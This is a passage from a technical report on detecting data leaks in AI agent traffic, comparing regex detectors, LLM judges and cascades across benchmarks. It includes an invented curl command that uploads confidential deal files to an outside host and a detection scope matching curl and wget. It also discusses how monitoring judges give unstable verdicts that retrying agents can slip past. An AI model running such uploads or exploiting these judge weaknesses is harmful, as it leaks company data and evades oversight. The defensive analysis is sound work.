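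Ayyagari fixed the model version and temperature, then ran four LLM judges ten times each on the same pairs of chatbot answers. On the 500 prompts of the Arena-Hard benchmark, two runs disagreed in 0.13% of comparisons for Claude Haiku 4.5, 3.57% for Claude Sonnet 4.6, 4.9% for Gemini 2.5 Pro and 5.16% for Claude Sonnet 4.5. Ayyagari suspects that the disagreements come from rounding differences and the way cloud services group requests, but did not isolate the cause. All four judges ran on a single cloud platform, so the rates may differ on others.

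The changes in verdict behind these averages were concentrated in close cases. Gemini changed its verdict at least once on roughly one comparison in eight. On those comparisons, two runs disagreed about 40% of the time, about what a split of seven runs to three would produce.

In *Behind Aggregate Scores*, Yorke (2026) found more variation with GPT-4.1. Rerunning the same judge at temperature 0 changed the outcome on 21.2% of 500 prompts, although the overall score moved by only about one point. Instructions that prioritised accuracy raised that share by 6.7 percentage points, and again the overall score barely moved. Editing a policy could therefore change which messages the judge flags even if the total stays the same.

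Ayyagari and Yorke both had judges choose the better of two answers, with ties allowed. Deciding whether a message breaks a policy is a different task. Judges may give steadier verdicts on clear leaks than on closely matched chatbot answers, but probably not on borderline transfers.

The usual remedy for inconsistent verdicts is to run the judge several times and take the majority verdict. This works well when the judge is already fairly consistent. If the runs are independent, a call that the judge flags on 95% of runs will be flagged by a majority of three about 99% of the time. A call that it flags on 70% of runs will be flagged by the majority only 78% of the time. Three runs also cost three times as much as one, and voting doesn't correct a mistake that the judge makes on every run.

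Unstable verdicts are a particular problem once a policy can block actions, because agents often retry. A judge with a 70% chance of blocking each attempt would let at least one of three attempts through about two-thirds of the time. Reusing the verdict for identical calls would prevent this, though the agent could still change the wording slightly and try again.

Fixing the model version helps only while the provider still offers that version. Ayyagari had planned to compare two versions of Gemini Pro, but the older one disappeared from the platform during the study. A company that changes its judge model effectively changes its policy, even if the text stays the same, and needs to test it again.

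The text being inspected can also influence the judge. Ayyagari cites Chen and Goldfarb-Tarrant (2025), who found that superficial features of a text changed safety verdicts even when its substance stayed the same.

### Stated confidence

A judge's confidence score is a reliable way to decide which verdicts need a human reviewer only if it is calibrated, meaning that verdicts with a stated confidence of 90% are correct about 90% of the time. Tian, Han and colleagues (2025) found in *Overconfidence in LLM-as-a-Judge* that the confidence of current judges significantly overstates how often they are right. A company that sends only low-confidence verdicts to reviewers would therefore miss many of the judge's errors.

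*Calibrating LLM Judges* (2025) estimated a judge's confidence with linear probes, small classifiers that read a model's internal states. These estimates were better calibrated than the model's stated confidence or estimates from comparing several of its answers, and they took about a tenth of the computing power. But probes need access to the model's internal states, and companies that rent a judge through a provider's API usually don't have it.

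A company can instead compare the judge's confidence scores with human verdicts on its own traffic. If reviewers find that verdicts scored at 0.9 are right 70% of the time, the company can treat a score of 0.9 as 0.7. This correction may not work for a different policy. *When Accuracy Gaps Fail to Certify* (2026) treats failure to transfer between tasks as a separate kind of calibration failure, and notes that earlier work on judges' confidence had not tested for it.

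Even a poorly calibrated score can be useful if correct flags tend to score higher than false alarms, because a threshold depends only on how the scores rank. *AgentLeak* (2026), a benchmark of leaks between cooperating agents, set its judge's threshold at 0.72 after a privacy specialist had labelled 200 segments of agent traffic. That value has no special meaning outside the benchmark.

### Exposure, cost and delay

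The judge has to read a message to check whether it leaks sensitive data, so if the judge runs at an outside provider, the check itself may be an external data transfer. The problem is smaller when the agent already runs on a model from the same provider under the same contract, because no new party receives the data. A company that uses Claude for its agents and Gemini for its judge may be adding a second recipient for everything the policy covers.

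Redaction can remove part of the exposure. Snowflake removes access keys and user identities from trajectories before its models assess them, but keeps the patterns that matter for the assessment. The judge could assess calls 1 and 2 with a label such as "AWS key" in place of the key. Redaction wouldn't work for the acquisition plans, because hiding what they reveal would also hide the reason for flagging them.

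Running the judge on the company's own servers avoids sending data to an outside recipient, but the model can't be too small. In the study by Meisenbacher and colleagues, the two smallest open models, with about a billion parameters each, had an agreement of 0.13 on how private a text was. The two largest, Llama 3.3 70B and Gemma 3 12B, reached 0.83 and agreed with people almost as closely as the commercial models did.

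Each verdict takes a model call, so cost and delay depend on how much traffic the policy covers. Speakeasy mainly advises narrowing the policy's scope. To catch data leaving through `curl`, a command-line program for web requests, it suggests checking only shell tool calls and asking the judge only about the intent of those commands. A narrower scope also excludes harmless messages that could cause false alarms. But if the agent sends the same data through an email tool outside the scope, the judge won't examine it.

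Snowflake saves money by screening with its cheaper model first, but a leak that this model misses never reaches the stronger one. Speakeasy's gateway, which inspects traffic between agents and their tool servers, checks only the first 50 KiB of each request or result, so large transfers need another control.

### Agreement with human judgement

Researchers have compared LLM judges with people on whether a message disclosed a particular piece of information and on whether the disclosure was appropriate. The judges do much better on the first question, which is closer to reading comprehension.

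Many of these studies report Cohen's kappa (κ), which corrects for agreement by chance:

κ = (p₀ − pₑ) / (1 − pₑ)

Here p₀ is the share of cases on which two raters agree, and pₑ is the share on which they would agree by chance. A value of 1 means perfect agreement, and 0 means agreement no better than chance.

Several benchmarks tested their judges on disclosure. *MuPPET* (2026) covers assistants in group conversations, and *PrivacyBench* (2025) covers personalised assistants that know users' secrets. *Privacy Disclosure Control Benchmark (PDC-Bench)* (2026) measures how specific a disclosure was. *BodhiPromptShield* (2026) rechecked the judge supplied with PrivacyLens, an older benchmark for agents.

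| Study | Human comparison | Agreement with the judge |
|---|---|---|
| *MuPPET* | 103 samples | 94–96%, κ 0.87–0.92 |
| *PrivacyBench* | 100 conversations, one reviewer | 93% |
| Fu and colleagues | Majority vote of three employees | 88% |
| *PDC-Bench* | 400 outputs, eight annotators | 87% for GPT-4o, 82% for Claude Sonnet |
| *BodhiPromptShield* | 120 decisions, two readers | 75–76%, κ 0.50–0.52 |

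The definition of a leak explains part of the spread. *PrivacyBench* told both the judge and the reviewer to count a leak only if the message revealed the core of a secret completely and explicitly. That leaves less room for disagreement, but it excludes hints and partial disclosures that a company might want to catch, some of which the judge flagged anyway.

Fu and colleagues found errors in the other direction. In 38 of the 43 cases where their judge disagreed with the human majority, it had missed a disclosure that people saw. A judge with that tendency would score well on precision while missing real leaks. In *AgentLeak*, a domain expert confirmed 94 of 100 leaks that the system had detected but didn't check the messages it hadn't flagged, so the result doesn't show how many leaks the system missed.

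The PrivacyLens judge did much worse on the recheck than in its original validation. *PrivAct* (2026), which reused the judge, restates the original result as 92% accuracy against four annotators on 153 cases, with a kappa of 0.82. The recheck deliberately drew cases from nine conditions, including some in which software had rewritten or masked the sensitive text. The five cases on which the two human readers disagreed all came from conditions in which software had rewritten the text. Agents often paraphrase, so a judge validated on plainly worded leaks may do worse on agent traffic.

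People also find it harder to judge whether sharing something is appropriate. Meisenbacher and colleagues had 677 people rate the sensitivity of their 250 texts and found an overall agreement of 0.39 (Krippendorff's alpha). The models matched the average human rating much better than individual ratings, and they tended to rate texts as more private than people did. Neither the models nor the people knew who would receive the text, so the study measured how sensitive the text was, not whether sharing it was permitted. When Fu and colleagues specified the recipient and the task, three employees with privacy training reached a kappa of 0.685 on whether sharing an item was appropriate.

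Tamber, Puri and colleagues (2026) ran the closest test of an agent judge in *PrivacyAlign*. They collected 3,516 annotations from 599 people on messages and other actions that agents had produced. Two annotators agreed on whether a response leaked sensitive information 78.4% of the time, for a kappa of 0.558. The researchers then carefully labelled 60 responses themselves and compared four judge models with those labels. The judges' average kappa was 0.45, against 0.62 for the majority vote of the annotators. GPT-5.5 scored highest of the four at 0.59, and Gemini 3.1 Flash Lite, Speakeasy's default judge in August 2026, scored 0.44.

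With only 60 responses, the ranking of the models is uncertain. The researchers also selected scenarios in which agents leaked, so the cases were probably harder than ordinary traffic. The judges had no company policy to apply, so they had to decide what people would generally consider inappropriate. A written policy can settle some of those questions in advance.

Worked examples may help an LLM judge apply a policy. When Tamber and colleagues showed judges another response to the same task, with people's labels and explanations, the average kappa rose from 0.45 to 0.54, and Gemini 3.1 Flash Lite's rose from 0.44 to 0.55. A company could add labelled examples to its policy, but the gain might be smaller because the examples would usually come from different tasks.

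## What side-by-side measurements on agent traffic show

Most results so far come from separate tests, in which secret scanners ran on source code and judges read messages that researchers had picked. A fair comparison requires running both kinds of check on the same agent traffic, which few studies do. The most detailed of these is an October 2026 study by Ogundoyin and Ikram, who built and tested RECONS, a filter that inspects what agents write and alters protected values before they reach a recipient who shouldn't have them.

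### How RECONS detects protected values

The study's 485 scenarios come from *AgentLeak*, which supplied the tasks, the agents' roles, the protected values and the rules on who may receive them. Ogundoyin and Ikram kept only scenarios in which at least two agents with different roles exchanged messages. The scenarios cover legal work (147), corporate work (138), finance (100) and healthcare (100). The open model Qwen3-32B ran the agents, and the tools returned prepared answers instead of contacting live services. The researchers recorded all seven channels described earlier.

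The conversations also follow a partial script. After the opening task, each turn is one of eight set types, such as a handoff or a closing summary. When one agent asked another to confirm a value, the turn disclosed that value 25.9% of the time. No other type of turn exceeded 2.7%. The mix of leaks therefore depends on how often the script includes these requests, and it may differ in real sessions like those Anthropic used to test the judge in Claude Code, its coding agent.

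RECONS searches the traffic in three tiers. Tier 1 uses pattern rules, checksums and named-entity recognition. Tier 2 is GLiNER, a model that looks for any entity types the user specifies, including types that weren't in its training data. Tier 3 is an LLM judge, Mistral-Small-24B, which looks for information with no fixed form, such as a passing reference to a pending lawsuit.

The LLM judge in RECONS reads final output, messages between agents, logs, and the free text in memory and files, but not tool arguments. Agents send data to outside services through tool arguments, which RECONS checks only with rules and entity recognition.

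### Recall by type of data

The researchers tuned the detector on 80 development scenarios and kept the other 405 for the final test. Before tuning, they measured how many protected values the rules and entity recognition found in the development scenarios.

| Type of value | Examples | Found | Recall |
|---|---|---|---|
| Value-sensitive | Names, addresses, amounts | 731 of 860 | 85.0% |
| Format-sensitive | Account numbers, other identifiers, dates of birth | 1,023 of 1,571 | 65.1% |
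| Context-sensitive | Diagnoses, legal strategies, internal assessments | 299 of 831 | 36.0% |

Recall was low for context-sensitive values, as expected, because most of them have no pattern for a rule to match. More surprisingly, recall was lower for format-sensitive values, which have a fixed format, than for names and addresses. This was partly because the detector lacked a rule for the format of local phone numbers and found only 19.6% of them. Adding that rule raised the figure to 99.3%. Together with other repairs, it brought recall to 73.0% on format-sensitive values and raised overall recall from 62.9% to 66.7%.

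Ogundoyin and Ikram measured the improvement on the same scenarios in which they had found the fault, so the 99.3% shows that the rule fits the phone numbers in this data set. A company whose phone numbers look different could get another result. The overall gain does seem to have carried over to the 405 held-out scenarios, where the tuned detector found 69.2% of the values that needed protection.

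The detector's precision is harder to measure. An automatic estimate put it at 15.7%, but this counted an alert as false unless it matched a value the study was tracking. The researchers inspected 40 of these supposed false alarms and found that 35% contained other sensitive data. If that sample is typical, about 45% of all alerts were correct. In most of the remaining errors, the detector had mistaken a field label for a value, or an agent name such as "A1" for personal data.

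### Recall in tool arguments

Recall also depended on which channel a value appeared in. The next table covers only format-sensitive values, so that differences in recall between channels don't simply reflect the kinds of data they carry.

| Channel | Recall before tuning |
|---|---|
| Messages between agents | 85.3% |
| Logs | 83.7% |
| Files the system produces | 79.3% |
| Final output | 73.7% |
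| Tool results | 71.6% |
| Writes to shared memory | 40.5% |
| Tool arguments | 39.2% |

The two lowest results come from the two channels that hold structured fields instead of prose. A likely explanation is that prose gives the detector more context. A rule or an entity model can use the words "Her account number is" to identify the digits that follow, while a tool argument may contain only the digits and a short field name.

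A company that tests its detectors on chat messages could therefore badly overestimate how well they protect its tool calls. In the final test, with RECONS running, 43.9% of the values it should have protected still got through in tool arguments, compared with 25.2% in messages between agents.

*AgentLeak* examined 100 scenarios for each of five models and found that agents passed unfiltered sensitive data to outside tools in 62% to 86% of them. In a set of scenarios without attacks, a filter on the final output cut leaks there from 48% to 1%. Leaks through shared memory and messages between agents stayed at 31%, because the filter didn't check those channels.

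### The judge's results

Ogundoyin and Ikram tested the RECONS judge separately on 60 items from the development scenarios. They chose 40 items that contained a protected value, including some that the other tiers had caught and some that those tiers had missed, and 20 that were harmless. The judge flagged 39 of the 40 and none of the harmless ones.

The judge's 97.5% recall and the 36.0% that the rules achieved on context-sensitive values come from different samples, so they are not directly comparable. The judge's sample is also small. Using 95% confidence intervals, catching 39 out of 40 leaks is compatible with a true recall as low as about 87%, and no false alarms out of 20 is compatible with a true false positive rate as high as nearly 17%.

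The 299 passages from the earlier worked example give a firmer estimate. The judge caught 30 of the 32 leaks in them and raised three false alarms. Exact and structured matching had failed to settle any of these passages. The two experts who labelled them agreed on 95.7% before discussing their differences. Gemma-3-27B, a judge from another model family, gave the same verdict as Mistral on 96.7%, so the choice between the two mattered little.

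However, this judge had an easier task than a company's judge would, because it compared each passage with a particular protected value and scored whether the passage expressed it. A judge that enforces a ban on external data transfer has no list of every secret, so it must detect that something is sensitive and then determine whether the policy forbids sending it.

The judge also missed leaks that a simple text search would have caught. RECONS rewrites context-sensitive passages to remove the protected fact, and the judge checks each rewrite. In the full test, it approved some rewrites that still contained the protected value word for word. With an exact-match check added, the scoring system still flagged seven altered passages, down from 67.

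Six of those seven involved values such as "no criminal history", where the judge counted any mention of the topic as a disclosure. In the seventh, the same judge gave different verdicts on identical text in two calls, even though its temperature was 0.

### Judge thresholds and detector rules

Ogundoyin and Ikram also tried *AgentLeak*'s threshold of 0.72 on their own 299 passages. They compared thresholds by F1, which combines precision (P) and recall (R) in one number:

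F1 = 2PR / (P + R)

F1 was 0.923 at a threshold of 0.5 and 0.853 at 0.72, the threshold borrowed from the other benchmark. Both thresholds raised three false alarms, but 0.5 caught 30 passages with leaks and 0.72 caught only 26. The two benchmarks used different judge models, and a score of 0.72 from one model need not mean the same as 0.72 from another.

Someone who sees a missed phone number can write a rule for its format, test it on examples and leave every other rule unchanged. But changing the judge's threshold affects every type of data at once, and only labelled examples can show whether the change helped. The sample contains 32 leaks, so each one changes recall by about three percentage points. A company would need many more leaks in its sample to choose reliably between similar settings.

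How useful a given threshold is also depends on how often leaks occur, which can vary widely between systems. Ogundoyin and Ikram ran the same scenarios with the same model on eight agent frameworks, the software that coordinates the agents. Leak rates ranged from 0.29% with Google ADK to 43.38% with AutoGen. If those were the shares of messages that leaked, a judge with the recall and false positive rate measured on the 299 passages would have a precision of about 20% with Google ADK and 98% with AutoGen.

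### Detecting a value and permitting its transfer

The earlier comparison of blanket redaction with a filter that checks the recipient comes from the final test of RECONS on 405 scenarios. The test counted how many unauthorised and authorised disclosures got through. The full results also cover Presidio and a version of RECONS with a fixed allowlist.

| Filter | Unauthorised disclosures that got through | Authorised disclosures kept |
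|---|---|---|
| Presidio, redacting what it finds | 35.5% | 34.7% |
| Blanket redaction | 28.3% | 20.5% |
| RECONS, checking the recipient | 29.25% | 94.1% |
| RECONS, with a fixed allowlist | 29.81% | 100% |

Blanket redaction and RECONS let through similar amounts because neither can act on a value that the detector misses. Of the 10,116 unauthorised disclosures that got past RECONS, 95.5% involved values that it had never flagged, so a better rule about recipients would have prevented few of them. Context-sensitive values again got through most often, at 55.7%, compared with 23.3% of format-sensitive values and 17.6% of value-sensitive ones.

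The large difference in authorised disclosures kept is based on much less data. The test contained 303 authorised disclosures. RECONS kept about 285 and blanket redaction kept about 62, and the gap comes almost entirely from 10 of the 405 scenarios. In the published results, a system with no filter also kept 0% of authorised disclosures, which is hard to reconcile with the definition, since a system that removes nothing should keep them all.

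Most of the advantage over blanket redaction seems to come from having a list of permitted values, rather than from checking the recipient. The fixed allowlist in the last row contains the values that a task may disclose and ignores who receives them. It kept every authorised disclosure and let through only 0.56 percentage points more of the unauthorised ones than the method that checks recipients.

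Checking recipients did help in a narrower test on the development scenarios. The allowlist let through 50 of the 2,092 detected values that the recipient should not have received, while the recipient check let through none. The researchers also tested a rule blocking any transfer whose recipient could in principle forward the value to someone unauthorised. They left it out because it would have stopped 14 of the 17 permitted transfers in the sample.

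The scoring is also weak because the same judge helps run the filter and measure its success, so a leak the judge fails to detect may count as prevented. An independent judge or a human check of the altered messages would give a more reliable figure.

Blocking too much also stops agents from doing their work. *AgentLeak* describes a prototype that masked any value a channel was not permitted to carry. In 120 scenarios, it cut leaks through shared memory and messages between agents from 31.5% to 2.4%, while task completion fell from 78.6% to 73.9%. In another 50 scenarios, where agents were forbidden to share any sensitive data with each other, completion rates were between 35% and 65%.

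### AgentLeak's three tiers

*AgentLeak* compares patterns and a judge more directly, by running each tier on the same 1,000 segments of agent traffic. Its judge was Qwen-2.5-7B, a much smaller model than the one in RECONS.

| Method | Precision | Recall | False positive rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| Planted markers only | 100% | 8.0% | 0.0% |
| Markers and structured patterns | 98.9% | 18.0% | 0.2% |
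| LLM judge only | 94.1% | 92.6% | 6.2% |
| All three tiers | 95.2% | 93.4% | 4.8% |

The benchmark's first method, labelled "regex only", searches for unique strings that the researchers planted in the protected data. Its 8% recall therefore mainly shows how often agents copied those strings, and the label could mislead someone comparing the method with a detector catalogue. The second method adds formats such as Social Security numbers, card numbers and medical diagnosis codes. A full catalogue would recognise more formats and might find more leaks, but it would still miss a diagnosis that an agent had described in ordinary words.

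In the leaks that the researchers analysed, agents often reworded the sensitive data. In one example, the agent wrote that a patient "is being treated for diabetes" instead of giving the diagnosis code. Planted markers caught 18 of the leaks, structured patterns caught 24, and the LLM judge caught the remaining 184, or more than 80%. The pattern tier also raised false alarms, because a ticket number such as `TIC-987-65-4321` contains what looks like a Social Security number.

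The published false positive rates are inconsistent. The table gives 4.8% for the full system and 6.2% for the judge alone, but if the system flags whatever any tier flags, it can't raise fewer false alarms than the judge. Elsewhere, the paper gives the judge's rate on the same 1,000 segments as 4.8%. It also reports 4.8% for a calibration set with 100 harmless segments, where every rate should be a whole percentage.

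These inconsistencies are too small to explain the gap between 18% and 93% recall. But they make the false positive rates a poor basis for estimating how many alerts a company's reviewers would face. RECONS isn't independent confirmation, because it reuses AgentLeak's scenarios and three-tier scoring method.

### Commercial detectors on tool calls

Li and Xu (2026), in *ToolMinimize*, tested detectors on tool arguments, where RECONS was weakest. ToolMinimize is software that rewrites a tool call so the tool receives only the data it needs. In their opening example, a user asks about the weather near their oncologist at Memorial Sloan Kettering, a cancer centre in New York. The agent sends the hospital's full name and address to a weather service that needs only the city. The hospital's name suggests a diagnosis, even though it doesn't identify the user.

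ToolMinimize looks for such clues with more than 40 regular expressions, rules for extracting entities, and lists of sensitive places and professions. Li and Xu ran it on 73 tool calls alongside Presidio and the detection services that Amazon and Google sell.

| Detector | Items found per call |
|---|---|
| ToolMinimize with an added entity-recognition model | 8.56 |
| ToolMinimize | 6.30 |
| Presidio | 4.70 |
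| Google Cloud DLP | 4.42 |
| AWS Comprehend | 3.30 |

These are counts of what each detector reported, so they measure neither recall nor precision. A detector could have the highest count because it raised more false alarms. People and models also disagree on how many sensitive items a call contains. In a check of 35 calls, the researchers' labels averaged 3.4 items per call, while GPT-4o averaged 5.3 and Claude averaged 7.6.

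The ranking is a poor guide to coverage. Without the added entity-recognition model, ToolMinimize found only 43.5% of direct identifiers, such as Social Security numbers, email addresses and phone numbers. The model raised that to 73.9% and added about 26 milliseconds per call.

Li and Xu also tested 20 harmless scenarios. The detector falsely raised an alert in four (20%), and the software changed tool calls unnecessarily in two (10%). Both rates are imprecise because there were so few scenarios, but they would be high for a check that runs on every tool call.

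An optional step uses GPT-4o to decide whether the user's task requires each item the detector found. This matters most for email. The basic version leaves the whole message body untouched because the email tool requires a body. GPT-4o can remove an irrelevant remark about a recent job loss and keep the rest.

Li and Xu used a "privacy cost" score, which weights each unnecessary item by its sensitivity and by how much the user can trust the recipient. The basic version reduced the score by 71.1%, and the version with GPT-4o reduced it by 90.9%. For map searches, the reduction fell from 100% to 80% because GPT-4o correctly kept addresses that the route needed. The GPT-4o step took about 800 milliseconds, compared with a median of 1.77 milliseconds for the basic version.

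GPT-4o examined only items that the rules had found, so it couldn't recover anything they had missed. The result is therefore better evidence of whether a language model can judge necessity than of whether it can find leaks.

### External transfers

A limited literature search found no study that runs a pattern detector and an LLM judge on the same external transfers and scores both against what a policy allows. Two studies compare the methods on other security problems, and their results differ.

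*Agentic Commerce Bench* (2026) covers payment fraud by AI agents. A pattern-based check caught 20% of the fraud with no false positives, and an LLM judge caught 26% with a false positive rate of 13.3%. When an agent's stated intention didn't match the payment it made, the judge caught 5% of the fraud and the pattern-based check caught 19%. The judge was given only the agent's reasoning, not the payment.

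*Detecting Malicious Agent Skills in the Wild using Attention* (2026) tested both methods on skills, which are add-on packages that agents load. Strict regular expressions found 19.0% of the malicious skills and an LLM judge found 47.6%, both without false alarms. Showing the judge only the ten most suspicious passages of each skill raised its recall to 57.1%. These percentages are consistent with a test set of just 21 malicious skills, in which case the patterns would have found four and the judge ten.

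Lin, Wu and colleagues (2026), in *AgentRaft*, studied data that agents send to third parties, but tested only LLM judges. They built four agents with functions from real tools and gave them requests that involved reading data and sending part of it elsewhere. In one case, a user asked an agent to email a payment date and amount to an auditor, and the agent also included the card number and its security code. For each piece of data, the judge had to decide whether the user had meant to send it or the task required it.

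The following results come from 100 requests to an office agent. The false positive rates follow from the published counts.

| Judge | Precision | Recall | False positive rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4.1 | 82.0% | 86.4% | 34% |
| DeepSeek-V3.2 | 79.7% | 88.2% | 40% |
| Qwen3-Plus | 78.4% | 89.9% | 45% |
| All three, voting | 97.6% | 98.2% | 4% |

Each judge, used alone, flagged at least a third of the data that the agent was right to send. In the tests of whether a protected value was present, the judges' false positive rates were between about 1% and 6%. The two sets of tests used different models and data, and Lin and colleagues sampled only requests in which the agent had overshared, which probably made the harmless items harder to tell apart from the overshared ones. The gap is still consistent with the earlier comparisons with human judgement, in which judges were better at spotting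 a disclosure than at deciding whether it was appropriate.

The voting result looks much better, but a simple majority of the three judges' votes can't have produced it. The judges raised 112 false alarms between them on 94 harmless items, so two or more judges must have wrongly flagged at least nine of the same items. The reported total for the voting system is only four. It must have used different runs or something beyond a majority vote, so a company that takes a simple majority of three judges can't count on the same improvement.

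## Combining detectors, judges and destination rules

The usual way to combine pattern detectors and LLM judges is a cascade, which runs the cheapest check first and moves to the next only if the result is inconclusive. Gowda describes Speakeasy's cascade, which starts with regular expressions and exact text matching, then uses a model that recognises names and addresses, and ends with an LLM judge. When an early check settles a message, the system avoids the delay and cost of a judge call.

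### What a pattern match can settle

Gowda supports this order by claiming that "most violations have a deterministic signature", meaning a fixed form that a rule can match, but gives no data. The evidence is mixed. In *AgentLeak*, the patterns missed more than 80% of the leaks found.

Ogundoyin and Ikram got a result closer to Gowda's claim. They ran 122,220 checks, each testing whether one channel in one run disclosed a particular protected value. Exact or structured matching found a disclosure in 57.5% of them, and only 29.9% needed the judge. But the software was given the value to look for. A company can provide such values only for data it has indexed, such as customer numbers.

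Even if most leaks have a recognisable form, a cascade works only if the early check is right about the messages it doesn't pass to the judge. Under a contextual policy, neither a pattern match nor the lack of one shows whether a message is a leak. The detector finds no match in call 3, the upload of the acquisition plans, but does match call 2, the routine storage of the AWS key.

If the judge reads only the messages the detector flags, it never reads call 3, which the detector doesn't flag. A cascade can instead send the judge every unflagged message, but that is almost all of them. Suppose a detector catches 60% of leaks and flags 1% of harmless messages. Among 100,000 messages with 100 leaks, it flags 60 leaks and 999 harmless messages. The other 98,941 go to the judge, so the cascade saves only about 1% of the judge's calls. The 999 false alarms also stand, because the judge never reviews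 them.

The cascade suits a policy that depends only on the form of the data. If a company bans private keys from all web requests, whatever the destination, a detector match is enough to establish a violation. If a policy depends on the recipient or the purpose, the judge must check all the traffic the policy covers.

### Flagging on either check or on both

A company that runs both a pattern detector and an LLM judge can flag a message if either one flags it, or only if both do. A cascade runs the detector first and sends only some messages to the judge. It flags the same messages as the "either" rule if it flags every match and sends the rest to the judge, and the same messages as the "both" rule if it sends only the matches to the judge.

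Take the detector above and an LLM judge with a recall of 90% and a false positive rate of 0.4%. These are invented figures. If the two checks make errors independently, then:

- either: recall is 1 − (0.4 × 0.1) = 96%, and the false positive rate is 1 − (0.99 × 0.996), or about 1.4%
- both: recall is 0.6 × 0.9 = 54%, and the false positive rate is 0.01 × 0.004 = 0.004%

The next table applies these rates to the same 100,000 messages.

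| Arrangement | Leaks caught, of 100 | False alarms | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|
| Detector alone | 60 | 999 | 6% |
| Judge alone | 90 | 400 | 18% |
| Either | 96 | 1,395 | 6% |
| Both | 54 | 4 | 93% |

Adding the detector to the judge catches six more leaks and raises 995 more false alarms, or about 166 for each extra leak. Requiring both checks to agree almost eliminates false alarms but misses nearly half the leaks.

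The detector and the judge probably don't miss leaks independently, because some messages are harder than others for both. Suppose the judge catches 90 of 100 leaks, and the detector catches only the 60 that have a recognisable form. If the 10 leaks the judge misses have no recognisable form, the detector misses them too, and flagging a message when either check flags it still catches 90. If the judge misses only credentials, perhaps because they are buried in long commands, the detector catches those 10 and the combination catches all 100.

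The same problem matters more for false alarms. Both checks can wrongly flag a made-up key in a tutorial, or call 2 if the judge can't see which AWS account receives the key. If the detector also matched every harmless message that the judge wrongly flagged, the "both" rule would raise 400 false alarms instead of 4.

*AgentLeak* provides enough data for a rough test of whether the two checks miss leaks independently. Its markers and patterns caught 18.0% of leaks and its judge caught 92.6%. If their misses were independent, the two together would catch 93.9%, which is close to the 93.4% the benchmark reports. The benchmark's false positive rates are too inconsistent for a similar test of false alarms. A company can test for independence by running both checks on the same labelled messages and counting how often they make the same mistake.

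On the four example calls, a judge with the precise policy and enough context correctly flags calls 1 and 3. The "either" rule also wrongly flags call 2, because the detector flags it. The "both" rule flags only call 1, and it can't catch any leak without a recognisable form, however good the judge is.

Requiring two checks to agree works better when the first is also a judge and is deliberately set to flag too much. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes such a pair. The second stage cut the false positive rate from 8.5% to 0.4% but also lowered recall.

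Symantec's *Secure Open-Source AI Agents with the DLP You Have Now* describes a proof of concept that blocks a tool call if either of two checks flags it. Symantec's DLP engine inspects the call first, followed by Llama Guard, a Meta model that classifies requests as safe or unsafe. In the demonstration, the DLP engine blocked a search containing a Singapore identity number. It later blocked a document being returned to the agent because the text contained the word "confidential". Llama Guard blocked a request about how to compromise a website.

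Symantec argues that neither check can replace the other, because a document's confidentiality depends on a label the company assigns, which a model can't infer from the text, while harmful intent depends on meaning. That is fair, but neither check tests whether the recipient is allowed to have the data. Llama Guard applies general safety categories, not the company's transfer policy, so the two checks would probably give calls 3 and 4 the same verdict.

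### Rules that choose what the judge reads

A rule can also select messages for the judge without deciding anything about them, as in Speakeasy's advice to judge only shell calls when looking for data that leaves through `curl`. Speakeasy writes scopes in CEL, a small language for logical conditions. The following scope adapts one of its examples:

`tool_calls.exists(t, t.function.matchText("bash") && t.args.get("command").matchRegex("curl|wget|https?://"))`

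It selects any message with a call to the `bash` shell whose command contains `curl`, the similar program `wget` or a web address. The judge might then read these two invented commands:

- `curl -O https://example.org/tool.tar.gz`
- `curl -F file=@/deals/heron-final.pdf https://files.example/upload`

The first downloads a software package and the second uploads the acquisition plans. A regular expression could distinguish uploads from downloads, but it couldn't determine whether the user had asked for this upload or whether the company controls the site. Selecting only uploads would also miss leaks, because a download request can carry a key in its URL.

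A selection rule should be broad, because any leak it misses never reaches the judge. Selecting a harmless command costs the company only one judge call and raises no alert. If the rule selects 95% of leaks and the judge catches 90% of those, overall recall is 85.5%. The scope above would miss, for example, a Python script that sends a file, or a `git push` to an outside repository whose address is stored in a settings file.

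The opposite design lists the actions that can skip the judge. In Claude Code's auto mode, these are file reads, searches and edits inside the project folder. All other actions go to the judge unless the user has set a rule allowing them, so the judge checks new tools by default. Anthropic also drops users' existing rules that allow all shell commands or scripting languages, because they would let the commands that can do the most damage skip the judge.

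Speakeasy also supports this approach. Gowda (2026), in *Reducing false positives in AI workflows*, describes writing a deliberately loose policy that covers everything, then exempting traffic known to be safe. Applying an exemption before the judge runs avoids the judge call, while applying it afterwards only suppresses the finding.

### Cost and delay

Suppose a company's agents produce 100,000 messages a day and 2% of them are shell calls that contact a host. Each judge call uses 2,000 input tokens and 100 output tokens. At illustrative prices of $1 per million input tokens and $5 per million output tokens, one call costs a quarter of a cent.

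The table's delay estimates are based on a demonstration in Matsuzaki's *Securing AI agents*, which timed Datadog's AI Guard while an agent read and summarised a GitHub issue. AI Guard ran six evaluations in one turn, taking 1.46 to 2.16 seconds each and 10.4 seconds in total. The table uses the average of 1.74 seconds and assumes that the agent waits for each verdict.

| | Judge every message | Judge selected shell calls |
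|---|---|---|
| Judge calls per day | 100,000 | 2,000 |
| Cost per day | $250 | $5 |
| Delay in a 50-message session | 87 seconds | 1.7 seconds |

The ratio of 50 to 1 comes entirely from the share of traffic that the rule selects, so a model three times as expensive would triple both costs without changing the ratio. The delay figures are less certain, because they come from one vendor's demonstration of its own product. Li and Xu's GPT-4o step took about 0.8 seconds, and using that figure instead would cut both delays by more than half.

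A slow check can also reduce recall. Speakeasy's gateway lets a call through if the scan can't finish in time. Symantec's proof of concept blocks the call if a check is unavailable, so an outage stops the agent's work.

Where a check runs limits what a judge can read, regardless of the company's budget. According to Matsuzaki, developers using Amazon's managed agent service can add their own check inside the function that carries out a tool call. That function receives the current call's details but not the conversation, so a judge there couldn't determine that the user had asked for call 4. Matsuzaki recommends Datadog's product for agents whose developers run the loop themselves, but the limitation comes from the data Amazon passes to the function.

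### Sorting matches by the surrounding text

The internet security company Cloudflare uses a language model to sort pattern matches without writing a policy for the model. Weaver, Shen and Johnson explain in *Improving Data Loss Prevention accuracy with AI-powered context analysis* that a US Social Security number can look like a taxpayer number, a bank account number or a phone number. Nearby keywords help tell these numbers apart, but people misspell them or leave them out.

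When a pattern matches, Cloudflare removes the matched value and converts the text around it into an embedding, a list of numbers that represents the text's meaning. Passages with similar meanings get similar embeddings, even if their wording differs. Cloudflare then finds the most similar passages among the customer's earlier matches. It lowers its confidence in the new match if administrators had marked those as false alarms and raises it if they had confirmed them as real.

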